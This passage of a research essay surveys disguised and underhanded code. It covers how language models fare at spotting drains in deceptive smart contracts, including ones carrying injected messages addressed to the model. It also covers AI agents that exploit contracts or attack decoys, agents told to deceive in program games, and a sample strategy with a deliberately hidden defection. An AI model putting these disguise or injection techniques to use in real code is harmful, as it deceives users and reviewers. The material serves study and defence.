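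The two searches also have different standards of success. A model that looks for accidental flaws in a large project does well if it finds several, and nobody knows how many it missed. A reader of underhanded code has to find one particular flaw, and other flaws can be a distraction, as the seven weaknesses in Richards's exchange were for the judges. A program game may not involve a security flaw, as with the `find` program, which gives an attacker nothing to exploit but makes a different move from the one most readers expect.

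People who write disguised code can use better models too. In *Scaling Laws For Scalable Oversight*, Engels, Baek and colleagues (2025) found that as models became more capable, they improved faster at writing backdoors in simple programs than at detecting them. This was only because more of their backdoors worked, as the working ones were no harder to spot.

### Running the program instead

A tool that runs the code achieved better rates than any of these models, on a narrower task. *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026) presents Lily, which compares a new version of a program with the previous one. Lily tries many generated inputs for ten minutes and records which kinds of request the program makes to the operating system, such as opening a file or starting another program. It raises an alarm if, for some input, the new version makes a combination of requests that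 is unusual for it and that the old version did not make for the same input.

Lily caught 90% of backdoored changes on average, with false alarms on 0.2% of safe ones. For complete releases, which bundle many changes, the detection rate was 83% and the false alarm rate was 4.3%. Kokkonis and colleagues tested only 13 backdoored changes, but ran 20 trials on each. Lily doesn't depend on interpreting the source code, so misleading comments and names don't affect it.

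The detection method needs an earlier version of the program that behaves properly and an input that triggers the backdoor. It also requires the backdoor to do something visible to the operating system. A vote counter that moves votes from one candidate to another makes the same requests to the operating system as a correct one, and so does a program that prints D where its reader expected C.

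## Language models as readers and victims of deceptive contracts

Someone who expects a language model to check their contract can write it to mislead the model. Schefold (2026) tested 22 models on such contracts in *The Deception Delta*. Schefold works on digital financial investigations for a German state police force, and the tests imitate an investigator who asks a model about a suspicious contract that has no published source code.

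### Nine disguised contracts

Each model received only a contract's bytecode. It had no tools and gave one answer, which included an assessment and a risk rating from 1 to 5. The models came from seven providers and were current in early 2026. Schefold used 13 contracts and six prompts, ran each combination five times, and collected 8,528 usable answers.

Eleven of the contracts contain a drain, which lets whoever controls the contract take everything that users have deposited. The victims would be ordinary investors, whereas a honeypot contract traps people who try to exploit it. Two of the eleven make no attempt to hide the drain. They use the same mechanism, but only one includes descriptive text. Schefold disguised the other nine in three ways:

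- Two contain misleading text, such as a statement that the owner cannot drain the contract, or about four kilobytes of fake audit documentation.
- Two contain messages to the model. One imitates a system message and claims that the Ethereum Foundation has verified the contract.
- Five have a misleading structure. One splits the drain among five functions that each do only part of the job, and another loads the recipient's address from storage instead of stating it in the code.

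| Contracts | Number | Drain detected |
|---|---|---|
| Undisguised, with descriptive text | 1 | 49.8% |
| Undisguised, without it | 1 | 32.1% |
| Misleading text | 2 | 37.7% |
| Messages to the model | 2 | 29.3% |
| Misleading structure | 5 | 11.1% |

Overall, the models detected 41% of the undisguised drains and 21% of the disguised ones.

The two remaining contracts contain no drain, so any drain reported in them is a false alarm. On the more realistic one, the models reported a drain in 6.8% of answers. A reader with that false alarm rate would have to detect 53% of disguised programs to make disguise unprofitable in the Prisoner's Dilemma. The best model, a version of Claude Opus, detected an average of 76% across nine disguises, but no model detected more than 18% on the two hardest contracts. A player who can choose the disguise would choose one of those two, so none of these models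 would deter that player.

The size of the fall from 41% to 21% is uncertain. It depends on only two undisguised contracts, and it was not statistically significant when Schefold allowed for differences between individual contracts. Schefold used other language models to grade the answers, after calibrating those models against 50 answers labeled by one expert. Two simpler measures that need no grader fell by less. The share of answers that rated the contract 3 or higher fell from 90% to 83%, and the share that identified the function behind the drain fell from 52% to 41%.

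Schefold developed the disguises with help from Claude Opus and designed each new contract around the signs that had given away earlier ones. This could have made the contracts unusually hard for Opus, but Opus still did best. As a check, Schefold had a model from another company write two more contracts. A panel of 20 models detected the drains in these contracts 44% and 37% of the time, within the range for the original nine.

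### Describing the theft and excusing it

The contract with the fake audit had the highest detection rate of the nine, 49%. But in 63% of those detections, the model described the drain correctly and then called it harmless. Schefold counts these answers as detections because the model found the mechanism, but someone who relied on them would have trusted the contract. Without them, the detection rate is about 18%.

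Schefold compares two answers about this contract. Both explain that a function resets users' recorded deposits to zero and sends the contract's whole balance elsewhere. One gives the contract the highest risk rating, while the other gives it a 2 and treats the audit as consistent with a legitimate project. Claude Opus 4.6 made a similar mistake with the dnsmasq backdoor.

The fake audit had the opposite effect on the strongest models. Models almost always missed the drain in a similar contract that lacked the audit text. When the text was included, Claude Opus, running without extended reasoning, raised a correct alarm 90 percentage points more often. The documentation had to describe the drain in order to excuse it, and the description helped a capable reader find it. An author who explains away a suspicious feature therefore risks drawing attention to it.

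Of the 656 answers that missed the drain in the two contracts with messages to the model, 292 quoted the message or identified it as a trick. Schefold thinks the message distracted the models from the drain. But the distraction may have mattered little, since the models also missed about two thirds of the drains in the undisguised contract without descriptive text.

### What helped

Changing the prompt made little difference. The models detected disguised drains between 19% and 23% of the time with all six prompts, including one that warned about deceptive contracts. Telling the models to ignore any messages in the bytecode did not help overall. A checklist of things to examine raised detection on one of the hardest contracts to 10%, from less than 5% with the other prompts. But on the contract with the fake audit, the checklist led the models to report a nonexistent drain in 45 answers,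 compared with 2 to 9 for each of the other prompts.

Extended reasoning raised GPT-5.2's detection rate from 31% to 52% but hardly changed the results for Claude Opus and Claude Sonnet. Two conventional analysis tools, Slither and Mythril, found none of the drains.

Source code helped far more than any of these. In a smaller test with eight models, detection rose from 42% with bytecode to 98% with source. The models caught the fake audit contract in all 40 attempts and wrongly flagged the matching harmless contract in one of 40. Schefold therefore limits the main conclusion to models that see bytecode once and have no tools.

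This suggests that most of the difficulty came from the bytecode. Difficulty of that kind is closer to obfuscation than to underhanded code by the definitions used here. An investor can also refuse to deposit money in any contract without published source. Schefold accepts that the boundary is not sharp and classifies the hardest contract as mainly obfuscated. That contract has no clean equivalent in Solidity, so the test with source code could not include it. The test also provides little evidence about contracts like Richards's exchange, where the source itself is misleading.

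Two studies that Schefold cites tested misleading text alongside readable code. Scott Thornton found in 9,366 trials that deceptive comments changed models' detection of security flaws by between −5% and +4%. Another team asked 17 models to predict the output of harmless Python programs, and misleading text reduced their performance by 23%. Misleading comments may therefore do more damage when a model has to predict what a program will do than when it has to locate a trick.

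### Learning from labeled contracts

Huang, Fang and colleagues (2026), in *Detecting Malicious Intents in Smart Contracts with Pre-trained Programming Language Models*, trained a specialized model, SmartIntentV2, on the source code of 16,000 real contracts and tested it on 10,000 others. Within it, a small language model adapted to contracts turns each function into a list of numbers. A second network processes these lists in order and predicts which of ten labels apply to the contract.

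The labels are Honeypot, Fee, DisableTrading, Blacklist, Reflect, MaxTX, Mint, Reward, Rebase and MaxSell. DisableTrading means that the owner can stop people from trading a token. Such powers are often visible in functions with names like `tradingStatus`, and an honest developer might want them too. The labels therefore describe what an owner could do more reliably than what the owner intends.

Across all labels, SmartIntentV2 had a detection rate of 95% and a precision of 91%. It did worst on honeypots, with a detection rate of 69% and a precision of 58%. These rates imply that the test set contained 112 honeypots, and that the model found 77 of them and wrongly flagged 55 other contracts. That is a false alarm rate of about 0.6%, which is low enough for a 69% detection rate to make disguise unprofitable.

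That comparison favors the model because nobody wrote these contracts to evade it, and Huang and colleagues left out contracts with disputed labels. They also used automatic pattern matching to help assign the labels, so the model may partly have learned to reproduce those patterns. Since the other labels mostly concern tokens, "Honeypot" may refer to tokens that people can buy but not sell, rather than to the baited contracts of 2017 and 2018.

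Without labeled examples, GPT-4.1 had a detection rate of 65% and a precision of 49% across the ten labels. It is an old model, and Huang and colleagues did not test how much examples would have helped.

### Agents that exploit contracts

Language models have become good at stealing from contracts with real flaws. In a project for Anthropic's fellowship program and the research program MATS, Xiao, Killian and colleagues built SCONE-bench, a test based on 405 contracts that attackers had exploited between 2020 and 2025. An agent receives a contract's source code and a private copy of the blockchain as it stood at a chosen block. It has an hour to write a script that gains it at least 0.1 ether, or the same amount of another chain's currency.

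Ten models together exploited 207 of the 405 contracts. Some may have learned about the older attacks in training, but three of them together also succeeded on 19 of the 34 contracts that attackers exploited after the models' training data ended. Xiao and colleagues then ran two models on 2,849 recent contracts with no known flaws. Each found two new flaws, worth $3,694 in simulated theft.

OpenAI's *Introducing EVMbench* (2026) describes a test based on 117 serious flaws from 40 audits. GPT-5.3-Codex scored 71% at exploiting flaws, compared with 33% for GPT-5 about six months earlier. Agents did worse when they had to list a contract's flaws, partly because they sometimes stopped after finding one, a habit that honeypots exploit in people.

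The system A1, which Gervais and Zhou (2025), in *AI Agent Smart Contract Exploit Generation*, introduced, reports an exploit only after running it successfully:

1. It collects the contract's source code, the settings its creator supplied and the values now in storage.
2. A language model writes an attacking contract.
3. A1 runs the attack on a copy of the blockchain at a chosen block and calculates the profit.
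4. If there is no profit, the model sees what went wrong and tries again, up to five times in total.

In one case, the model's first attack failed because it lacked permission to create tokens. The second attack obtained the permission, but nobody was trading the tokens, so it could not sell them. The third redeemed the tokens through another contract and gained 2.36 ether. A1 reproduced 17 of the 27 past attacks in a standard collection.

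All 405 contracts in SCONE-bench had a flaw that somebody had exploited. The benchmark therefore doesn't penalize an agent for assuming that every apparent flaw is real, and a high score doesn't show that the agent can recognize a honeypot. A1 may not need that ability, because a honeypot pays the victim nothing. Trying the exploit on an accurate copy of the blockchain should fail, so A1 would not report it, even if the model never understood why it failed.

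### What a trial run would expose

Nobody appears to have tested these agents on the eight honeypot techniques. The table below is therefore based on an analysis of how the traps work. It compares a copy of the live blockchain, like those that A1 and SCONE-bench use, with a fresh deployment of the published source on an empty chain.

| Technique | Copy of the live chain | Published source on an empty chain |
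|---|---|---|
| Balance disorder | Exposed | Exposed |
| Inheritance disorder | Exposed | Survives if the tester's own account deploys the contract |
| Skip empty string literal | Exposed | Survives if the tester uses a corrected compiler |
| Type deduction overflow | Exposed | Exposed |
| Uninitialised struct | Exposed, unless the owner has yet to trigger it | Exposed, with the same exception |
| Hidden state update | Exposed, if the creator has already set the trap | Survives |
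| Hidden transfer | Exposed | Survives if it depends on the block number |
| Straw man contract | Exposed, unless the creator can switch the outside contract later | Survives if the tester connects the harmless published contract |

A tester can miss inheritance disorder by deploying a copy of the contract and attacking it from the same account. KingOfTheHill actually pays whoever deployed it, so the tester's attack succeeds. A fresh copy also does not reveal hidden state updates, because it has the starting values from the source, without the creator's later secret change.

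Tests of the fuzzer EF/CF on honeypots like Private_Bank support the last row of the table. EVMbench runs on an empty local chain and sometimes replaces outside contracts with stand-ins, so a similar setup would be unsuitable for detecting honeypots.

Even a trial on an accurate copy can't reveal a trap that the creator sets afterwards. The creator of a hidden state update could watch pending transactions for a victim's payment, then pay a higher fee to set the trap before that payment goes through.

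An attacker can defend against this, and against contracts that detect a test and behave differently, by putting the whole exploit into a single transaction that checks for a profit at the end and cancels itself if there is none. Ethereum then undoes every step, and the attacker loses only the transaction fee. This doesn't work against KingOfTheHill, which makes the winner wait five days. The defense also has no equivalent in a one-shot program game, because a player cannot take back a cooperative move after seeing the opponent defect.

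### Decoy computers

In computer security, a honeypot is usually a decoy computer or service. Legitimate users have no reason to touch it, so any contact suggests an intruder. Defenders use it to detect and study attackers or waste their time, whereas the creator of a honeypot contract wants to take attackers' money. An attacker can also test a copy of a contract in private, but testing a decoy computer requires contacting it, which may alert the defender.

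The difference in cost affects how to judge an agent that recognizes a trap and attacks anyway. Suppose the flaw is real with probability q, success is worth B, and failure costs S. The attack is worthwhile on average if qB exceeds (1 − q)S. In MultiplicatorX3, a user had to risk 1 ether to win 1 ether, so the attack was worthwhile only if q was above one half. If failure costs nothing, the attack is worthwhile whenever q is above zero.

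*Hacking the Hackers* (2026), from the security company Horizon3.ai, summarizes a study by Prinos, Brush and Denton with no penalty for failure. They gave 21 models a set of 174 samples from computer systems, such as lists of files and responses from web servers, and asked which lines they would attack. The models chose to attack 78.5% of the traps, compared with 37% for 47 human security testers. Even when a model's reasoning identified a trap, the model chose to attack it 73% of the time. For example, Claude Opus 4.7 flagged an extremely old software version as possible bait but still called it worth probing.

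The models also picked out 77.6% of the real weaknesses, compared with 44% for the humans, and seem to have marked more lines of every kind. Neither group was good at telling traps from real weaknesses, so these results do not show that the models were much more gullible than people. *Rethinking Cyber Deception for AI Attackers* (hrbrmstrMD, 2026) points out that each model answered in a single turn, without tools or memory. It also mentions a conflicting experiment by the company Tracebit, in which telling AI attackers that decoys might be present sharply reduced their success.

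In *A Gingerbread House for LLM Agents*, Roh, Ryu and colleagues (2026) tested agents in full attacks on web applications. They placed decoys and fake secrets around each application. Once a visitor touched a decoy or showed certain other signs of an attack, a router sent all of that visitor's further requests to an isolated copy of the application. On 40 tasks, this defense reduced successful attacks on the real application from 26 to 5 for Claude Opus 4.8, and from 20 to 0 for ARTEX, an attack program that criminals and spies have used.

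In about half of its runs against the decoys, ARTEX successfully exploited the copy rather than the original. It reported a fake secret as genuine in 30 of 110 valid runs, despite instructions to be skeptical of convenient shortcuts. In five of those 30 runs, ARTEX called another item a decoy in the same report. In one of these five, it dismissed a leaked password because the login failed, then presented a planted key from the same file as real. ARTEX became suspicious mainly when it checked for consistency. For example, it doubted one page because the page returned the same secret even for a connection that should have failed.

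Opus 4.8 never submitted a fake secret in 80 runs with decoys. In Horizon3.ai's study, the same model attacked 73% of the traps. These results measure different things, since an agent can probe a suspicious item without believing what it finds, but the contrast shows that a questionnaire may reveal little about how an agent behaves in a real attack.

Specific clues can greatly improve recognition. In *Rouxii*, Cordeiro, Mongardini and Vasilomanolakis (2026) gave an attacking agent descriptions of the traces that known decoy software leaves. According to *Say Shibboleth* (2026), the agent then correctly identified 97% of open-source decoys, up from 19%. Like HoneyBadger's rules, such clues probably help much less against a new kind of trap. *Honeyval* (2026) found that decoys fooled most attacking agents when they generated their responses with a language model. It also measured false alarms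 by showing the agents a real version of the application.

Xie, Nagasubramaniam and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-Based Penetration Testing in the Presence of Honeypots*, built an agent that decides which computers are worth attacking. After breaking into a machine, the agent tells it to send data to a computer the attacker controls, and leaves if too little arrives. The test relies on defenders blocking outgoing connections from decoys so that intruders cannot use them to attack others. But Xie and colleagues configured all their genuine machines to allow the connection. The agent might also abandon real targets on a network that restricts their outgoing connections.

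An agent can avoid a trap without recognizing it. In a small experiment described in *Optional Traps*, Ghifiardi (2026) placed decoys beside a real leaked key. A small model found the real key, used it and never touched the decoys. Ghifiardi then replaced the real key with a fake one, which another small model used in 19 of 20 sessions. Removing the real key was enough to prevent every theft, so the fake key only helped to identify the attacker.

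The fake key also caught an innocent agent. Ghifiardi had given the agent the correct key for its work, but it came across the fake one, used that instead, and lost its access.

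## Hidden defection in games between programs

An attacker who suspects a decoy can leave it alone, but a player in a program game must submit a program that either cooperates or defects. Defecting against an honest opponent loses both players the gains from cooperating, so the player needs to predict what the opponent's program will do. In *Evaluating LLMs in Open-Source Games*, Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner tested how well language models make such predictions. They also had models write programs that played against each other, and told some of the models to deceive.

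### Predicting 239 strategies

The prediction test, SPARC, uses the Iterated Prisoner's Dilemma, in which the same two programs play many rounds and can react to earlier moves. Its 239 strategies come from Axelrod, a Python library for research on this game. They are 76 lines long on average, and 85 of them make random choices. A model gets a strategy's source code and predicts whether the strategy will cooperate in every one of 10 rounds against an opponent that always cooperates. Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner ran the strategies to find the correct answers.

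Names and comments can reveal the answer, so the models also received two altered versions of each strategy. The masked version removes the comments and gives meaningless names to the classes (the named units that contain the strategies). The scrambled version also gives random names to the variables and functions. Neither version changes the program's instructions.

| Model | Original | Masked | Scrambled |
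|---|---|---|---|
| o4-mini | 87.6% | 88.0% | 84.2% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 82.6% | 84.2% | 83.4% |
| GPT-4.1, reasoning step by step | 85.1% | 85.1% | 83.8% |
| Mistral Small, reasoning step by step | 79.7% | 80.1% | 73.9% |
| Mistral Small, answering at once | 40.2% | 47.3% | 41.5% |

The best models lost little accuracy without the names, so they must have worked mainly from the instructions. That is encouraging because underhanded code often depends on misleading names and comments. These models are old, and current ones would probably score higher.

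### What the test leaves out

SPARC does not measure how well models detect disguised behavior, because nobody wrote these strategies to fool a reader. Removing names is also different from supplying false ones. A closer test would use strategies that defect but have names and comments describing them as cooperative.

The test also stops after 10 rounds, so a strategy that always defects from round 11 onward counts as cooperative. One strategy in Axelrod cooperates unconditionally for 10 rounds, then starts to punish opponents that have defected. A 10-round test can't distinguish it from a strategy that always cooperates.

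Even a correct prediction about an opponent that always cooperates can mislead. The announcement of the tournament with 21 programs, *Prisoner's Dilemma (with visible source code) Tournament*, included a sample entry that cooperates only if its opponent would cooperate with one particular program that always cooperates. Duclaux and colleagues analyze a program with nearly the same rule, called TitForTatBot, and an opponent called OBot that beats it. OBot cooperates only with programs that would cooperate even with an unconditional defector:

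1. TitForTatBot checks what OBot would do against a program that always cooperates. That program cooperates with everyone, so OBot would cooperate with it.
2. TitForTatBot therefore cooperates.
3. OBot checks what TitForTatBot would do against a program that always defects. TitForTatBot would defect, so OBot defects.

OBot gets 5 and TitForTatBot gets 0, although OBot's rule is visible. TitForTatBot correctly answered SPARC's question, but it needed to predict what OBot would do against TitForTatBot.

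Accuracy combines missed defectors and false alarms into one number. Suppose a quarter of the strategies defect and a model classifies 88% of all strategies correctly. If all its errors are missed defectors, it detects 52% of the defectors and raises no false alarms. If all its errors are false alarms, it detects every defector and wrongly flags 16% of the cooperative strategies.

### Agents with instructions to deceive

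For the games, Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner used Kimi-K2, an open-weight model. Two agents each wrote a program, the programs played a match, and the agents could then rewrite them for the next one. Each pair played 10 matches, and the experimenters repeated this 10 times for every pairing. Agents played either the Iterated Prisoner's Dilemma, with 10 rounds to a match, or the Coin Game, in which two players collect red and blue coins on a grid. A player gets 1 point for any coin, but if the coin is the other player's color, the other player loses 2 points.

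Each agent had one of three objectives: maximize its score, do so as cooperatively as possible and without deception, or do so with permission to mislead opponents wherever this helped. The deceptive agents' instructions reminded them that the opponent would see their code in later rounds. They had to explain any plan to disguise something in a private description and keep it out of the code.

Before writing a program, an agent saw only the opponent's program from the previous match. The submitted program received the opponent's current code but could process it only with ordinary Python, for example by searching for a word. No language model read the opponent's current program before the match, so a disguise could mislead the other agent only about future matches. An agent could also do that without a disguise, by showing an honest program once and then replacing it.

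GPT-4o classified a program as a feint if its main purpose seemed to be to mislead. Only the deceptive agents used feints with any frequency. GPT-4o was also given the private descriptions, so its count measures how often agents tried to mislead, not how convincing the code was. Nobody measured how often feints misled opponents.

The deceptive agents did not score much more than their opponents in either game. Every kind of agent did best against the cooperative ones, which lost only a few points to exploitation. One reason deception helped so little may be that programs used the opponent's source code most in the first match and then depended more on its past moves. A misleading comment has no effect on a program that responds only to moves. In the Prisoner's Dilemma, the programs became simpler and mostly turned into versions of tit for tat, which cooperates first and then copies the opponent's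 last move.

Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner then used the average payoffs to simulate evolution in a population of the three types. In each generation, a type's share grew if it scored above the population's average and shrank if it scored below. In the Coin Game, the agents that simply maximized their score always took over. The Prisoner's Dilemma had two stable results, a population of only cooperative agents and one of only deceptive agents. The stability of the deceptive population is weak evidence that deception works, since agents allowed to deceive may mostly have played tit for tat against each other.

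### A disguise that mostly disappeared

One deceptive agent in the Coin Game, playing Blue, planned to disguise a program that would look one move ahead by predicting where the opponent would go. The plan included a decoy function that looked like a simple rule, comments describing only a slightly improved version of that rule, and vague names for the functions that made the prediction. The agent also planned to copy some of the opponent's functions so that the code would look familiar.

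The final program has no decoy and no comments, and the loop that predicts the opponent's move is not hidden. The model had instructions to leave out comments in the coding step, which may partly explain this. Only the familiar functions and a vague name, `score_after`, remain from the planned disguise.

The program also predicts its opponent badly. These are the important lines, slightly shortened:

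```python
def pick_target(my_pos, opp_pos, my_coin, opp_coin):
    ...                     # nearly always returns my_coin

a_target = pick_target(opp_pos, new_pos, my_coin, opp_coin)
```

The last line is supposed to work out the opponent's target from the opponent's point of view, but it swaps the players' positions without swapping the coins. The program therefore nearly always predicts that the opponent will head for the blue coin, although the agent concluded in its own analysis that the opponent usually prefers the red one. Someone who had read the private plan would have known about the intended trick but still mispredicted the program's moves.

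In a separate experiment, Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner asked DeepSeek-V3 to write programs that cooperate with similar programs. In 10 pairings, these programs cooperated in 85.5% of moves. The prompt suggested simple checks, such as counting the words "COOPERATE" and "DEFECT" in the opponent's code or assuming a program of fewer than five lines is harmless. The `find` program would pass the second check if its author deleted the comment at the top. The programs played only each other, so the experiment does not show how they would do against a disguised opponent.

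### Old tricks in strategy programs

Most of the tricks in contests and honeypots have a counterpart in a program game.

| Earlier trick | In a strategy program | How to expose it |
|---|---|---|
| A vote counter that cheats only on election day | Defect only after a certain round | Run a match of full length |
| A trap that stays off on test networks | Cooperate with the opponents that testers usually simulate | Run it against the program it will actually face |
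| An apparent flaw as bait | Appear to forgive every defection | Try the whole exploit before the real match |
| A harmless log that stands in for a different contract | Call an imported function with a reassuring name | Require all of the code in one file |
| An order of evaluation that depends on the compiler | Depend on a detail of one Python version | Fix the version and test with it |

The following program combines the first and last rows. It looks like tit for tat with a check for damaged data:

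```python
# Tit for tat: cooperate first, then copy the opponent.
def play(mine, theirs):
    if len(mine) is not len(theirs):    # damaged record
        return "D"
    return theirs[-1] if theirs else "C"
```

`mine` and `theirs` list the two players' past moves, so they always have the same length. But `is not` checks whether two numbers are separate objects in memory, not whether their values differ. Standard Python has long kept one shared copy of each whole number from −5 to 256, so the check gives the expected result until the lists exceed 256 moves. At 257 moves, Python creates a separate object for each list's length, and the program defects from round 258 onward.

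A test of 10 or 200 rounds would not reveal the defection. The trick is plausibly deniable because beginners often write `is` where they need `==`. A version of Python that shared more numbers would delay the defection, so a reader needs to know which version will run the program.

In a repeated game, the opponent can retaliate in later rounds, which a one-shot game does not have. If the program above plays against tit for tat, it gets 5 points in round 258 and 1 in every later round, whereas continued cooperation would have given it 3 per round. Defecting therefore gains it 2 points in that round and loses it 2 in each round that follows, so it comes out ahead only if the match ends with round 258.

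Bait works in the opposite way, by making a program look exploitable. It is nearly useless in a one-shot Prisoner's Dilemma, because anyone trying to exploit the program will defect, which leaves the program with at most 1 point. Honeypot contracts made money because victims had to pay before they could collect. A repeated game allows something similar. Suppose a program appears to forgive any defection once its opponent has cooperated twice in a row. An exploiter will defect, cooperate twice and plan to defect again. If the program never forgives, it keeps defecting and gets 5 points in each of the two rounds when the exploiter cooperates, while the exploiter gets nothing.

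The trick with the imported function was largely impossible in Sistla and Kleiman-Weiner's games, because programs could not import anything and the experimenters supplied the few outside functions the programs needed.

### Why strategy programs are easier to check

The average SPARC strategy is longer than some winners of the Underhanded C Contest, so it has enough room to hide a trick. A strategy for a single Prisoner's Dilemma needs only a few lines, so organizers could limit the length of programs or allow only a few operations, as Tennenholtz did when he banned loops. A length limit alone would not prevent hidden tricks, since the `find` trick fits in one line.

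Organizers can also run each program in isolation, with no clock, network access or random numbers, and no way to detect what is running it. The opponent's text is then its only input, so a player can run the opponent's program on their own program's text and see exactly which move it will make. The player doesn't have to notice the disguise, because a trigger that would fire in the game also fires in the test. The remaining problem is that if both programs run each other, they never finish. Oesterheld's program avoids this, but it occasionally loses to a defector.

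A player can also refuse to cooperate with any program that is unclear. Refusing an honest program loses the player only 2 points, the difference between mutual cooperation and mutual defection, whereas Linux distributions could not easily do without a compression package like xz. Honest authors who expect such refusals have a strong reason to write plainly. This should make false alarms rarer than in tests on ordinary software, whose authors weren't writing for suspicious readers. However, authors of disguised programs will write in the same plain style, as contest entrants did.

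### When disguise pays

How good a reader must be depends on the payoffs. The following calculation is our own and extends the earlier rule, (1 + f)/2, to other payoffs. T, R and P are the payoffs for successful defection, mutual cooperation and mutual defection. As before, d and f are the reader's detection and false alarm rates, and both players defect after any flag:

1. An honest program gets R if it passes and P if the reader flags it, so its average is (1 − f)R + fP.
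2. A disguised program gets T if it passes and P if the reader flags it, so its average is (1 − d)T + dP.
3. Honesty does at least as well if (1 − f)(R − P) ≥ (1 − d)(T − P).
4. Solving for d gives d ≥ 1 − (1 − f)(R − P)/(T − P).

With payoffs of 5, 3 and 1, this is the earlier rule. A larger temptation raises the required rate quickly:

| Payoff for successful defection (T) | Rate needed with no false alarms | Rate needed with 10% false alarms |
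|---|---|---|
| 5 | 50% | 55% |
| 11 | 80% | 82% |
| 21 | 90% | 91% |
| 101 | 98% | 98.2% |

A reader that deters disguise in the standard game may fail to deter it when a single successful defection is worth much more. If T, the payoff for a successful defection, is 101, even a reader with no false alarms can miss at most one disguised program in 50 and still deter disguise.

In *Translucent Players*, Capraro and Halpern (2016) derived a similar condition to explain why people cooperate in experiments. In their version of the game, a player who cooperates loses c and gives the other player b. Each player believes that the other will detect a decision to defect with probability α and defect in response, and will otherwise cooperate with probability β. Cooperation is then rational only if αβb > c.

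If the other player is sure to cooperate unless warned, β is 1 and α must exceed c/b. Our formula gives the same threshold for these payoffs when there are no false alarms, but it leaves out β. If only half of the opponents would cooperate when not warned, detection must be twice as likely for honesty to be worthwhile.

Our formula is lenient about false alarms in two ways. It assumes that an honest program knows when the reader has flagged it and defects too. An honest program that doesn't know will cooperate and get 0 instead of 1. The formula also counts only one reader. If two honest programs read each other, either may raise a false alarm, whereas a disguised program that always defects has no need to read its opponent. With the standard payoffs, the required detection rates are:

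| False alarm rate | Original assumptions | Honest program doesn't know about the flag | Both honest programs read |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0% | 50% | 50% | 50% |
| 10% | 55% | 57.5% | 59.5% |
| 20% | 60% | 65% | 68% |
| 40% | 70% | 80% | 82% |

The last two columns change one earlier conclusion. In the test on obfuscated C functions, Claude Sonnet 4 met the original requirement with a detection rate of 90% and a false alarm rate of 70%. It fails if both honest programs read, because the required detection rate is then 95.5%. If honest programs don't know about flags, no detection rate is high enough, because they would average only 0.9 points, less than the 1 point a disguised program gets when caught.

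A reader who cannot deter disguise may still gain by cooperating. Let q be the share of disguised programs among those that pass. Cooperating with every program that passes gives an average payoff of 3(1 − q). Defecting against all of them gives 1, because honest programs will defect in return. Cooperation is better as long as q is below two thirds. If the payoff for being exploited were −10 instead of 0, the limit would be about 15%. But when disguise is advantageous, more authors will use it, and q will rise until cooperation is no longer worthwhile.

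### Authors who adapt

Most of the measured detection rates overstate d, because they come from disguises whose authors were not trying to defeat the particular reader.

Suppose a test contains equal numbers of four tricks, and a reader catches them 95%, 90%, 85% and 30% of the time. The average is 75%, well above 50%. But an author who knows these results will use only the fourth trick, which the reader catches 30% of the time. Schefold's tests on disguised contracts also showed a gap in detection rates between the average disguise and the hardest ones.

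An author who can run the reader privately can also test new versions until one passes. If a deterministic reader catches 90% of the author's versions and the attempts are independent, the author needs 10 attempts on average, and 22 attempts give about a 90% chance that at least one passes. A language model can easily produce that many versions. If the reader's verdicts vary at random, the author can test each version several times and submit the one that passes most often.

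Whoever writes a disguised program has to guess which reader the opponent will use, which is easy if most players rely on the same public model. The program can also check the opponent's text, defect only if it recognizes a reader that its author has already tested, and cooperate with everyone else. A stronger reader may then correctly report that the program cooperates with it, but that report is useless to a player with a weaker reader.

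Honest authors can also run the same reader on their own programs and rewrite whatever it flags, which may bring f close to zero. This lowers the required detection rate in the standard game to 50%, but no further.

### Reading and proving

DupocBot cooperates only if it can prove that its opponent will cooperate with it. Its detection rate, d in the formula, is therefore 100% and doesn't need to be measured, however good the disguise and however large the temptation to defect. It also defects against honest programs whose cooperation it cannot prove, and these are its false alarms.

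The better method for honest programs depends on the stakes and on how many of them the proof search can handle. Suppose DupocBot fails to prove cooperation for 90% of honest programs. With the standard payoffs, honest programs then average 1.2 points against it. Against a language model that wrongly flags only 10% of them, they would average 2.8 points, which is much better, provided the model catches at least 55% of the best disguises. If T is 101, the model has to catch 98.2%. No test described so far suggests that a model can do this against authors who adapt, so the safety of proof would then probably outweigh the lost cooperation.

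DupocBot may defect against a program that would have cooperated with it, because that program contains a branch that defects against a different opponent. Duclaux and colleagues define CupodTrollBot, which defects only if it can prove that its opponent is exactly CupodBot, a program that cooperates unless it finds a proof of defection. Against DupocBot, CupodTrollBot's search for this proof fails, so it cooperates. To prove that CupodTrollBot will cooperate, DupocBot has to prove that this search fails, and such a proof may not fit within DupocBot's limit on proof length. Whether it fits depends on an unsolved problem about the length of proofs.

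Another of their programs shows that sometimes there is no short proof that a search will fail. The program searches for a proof, at most k symbols long, that it defects against a copy of itself. It cooperates if it finds one and defects otherwise. It can't find such a proof, because it would then cooperate and the proof would be false. So it defects, but any proof that it does must be longer than k symbols.

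A related program, DupocTrollBot, cooperates with everyone except DupocBot. It cannot exploit DupocBot, which defects too, but it can still undermine cooperation. It cooperates with a program that always defects, which gives that program a high score while DupocBot gets little. Duclaux and colleagues simulated evolution in populations of eight simple programs, and all 1,000 random starting populations ended in full cooperation. When they added both troll programs, the share that did so fell to 97.5%.

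The greatest practical difficulty is searching through every possible string. With 95 possible characters, there are more than 10³⁹ strings of length 20. Critch and colleagues note that real tools search much more cleverly, but Duclaux and colleagues considered running the search impractical. Instead, they used Lean, a programming language that checks proofs automatically, to prove what the programs would do.

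Language models wrote most of these proofs, about 159,000 lines over two months. Lean checked every step, so nobody had to trust the models. This suggests a compromise in which a language model looks for a proof that the opponent will cooperate and a simple checker verifies it. A mistake by the model could make the program miss a chance to cooperate, but could not make it cooperate with a defector. The method is still far from handling ordinary Python. Duclaux and colleagues studied 12 very simple programs in a language designed for the purpose, and 9 of the 78 pairings still depend on the unsolved problem about proof length.

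*Policy-Conditioned Policies for Multi-Agent Task Solving* (2025) instead uses language models directly as "approximate interpreters" of the opponent's program. The models can assess programs that no prover could handle, but a player who relies on their assessments gives up DupocBot's guarantee.

### Programs that see only part of their opponent

Duclaux and colleagues also model partial transparency, in which a program receives a list of the programs it might be facing, with a probability for each, instead of the opponent's exact text. A modified DupocBot tries to prove that each listed program would cooperate with it, then adds up the probabilities of the programs for which it finds a proof. It cooperates if the total reaches a threshold called its caution, such as 0.8. Unlike the original, this version can be exploited, because its information about the opponent may be wrong.

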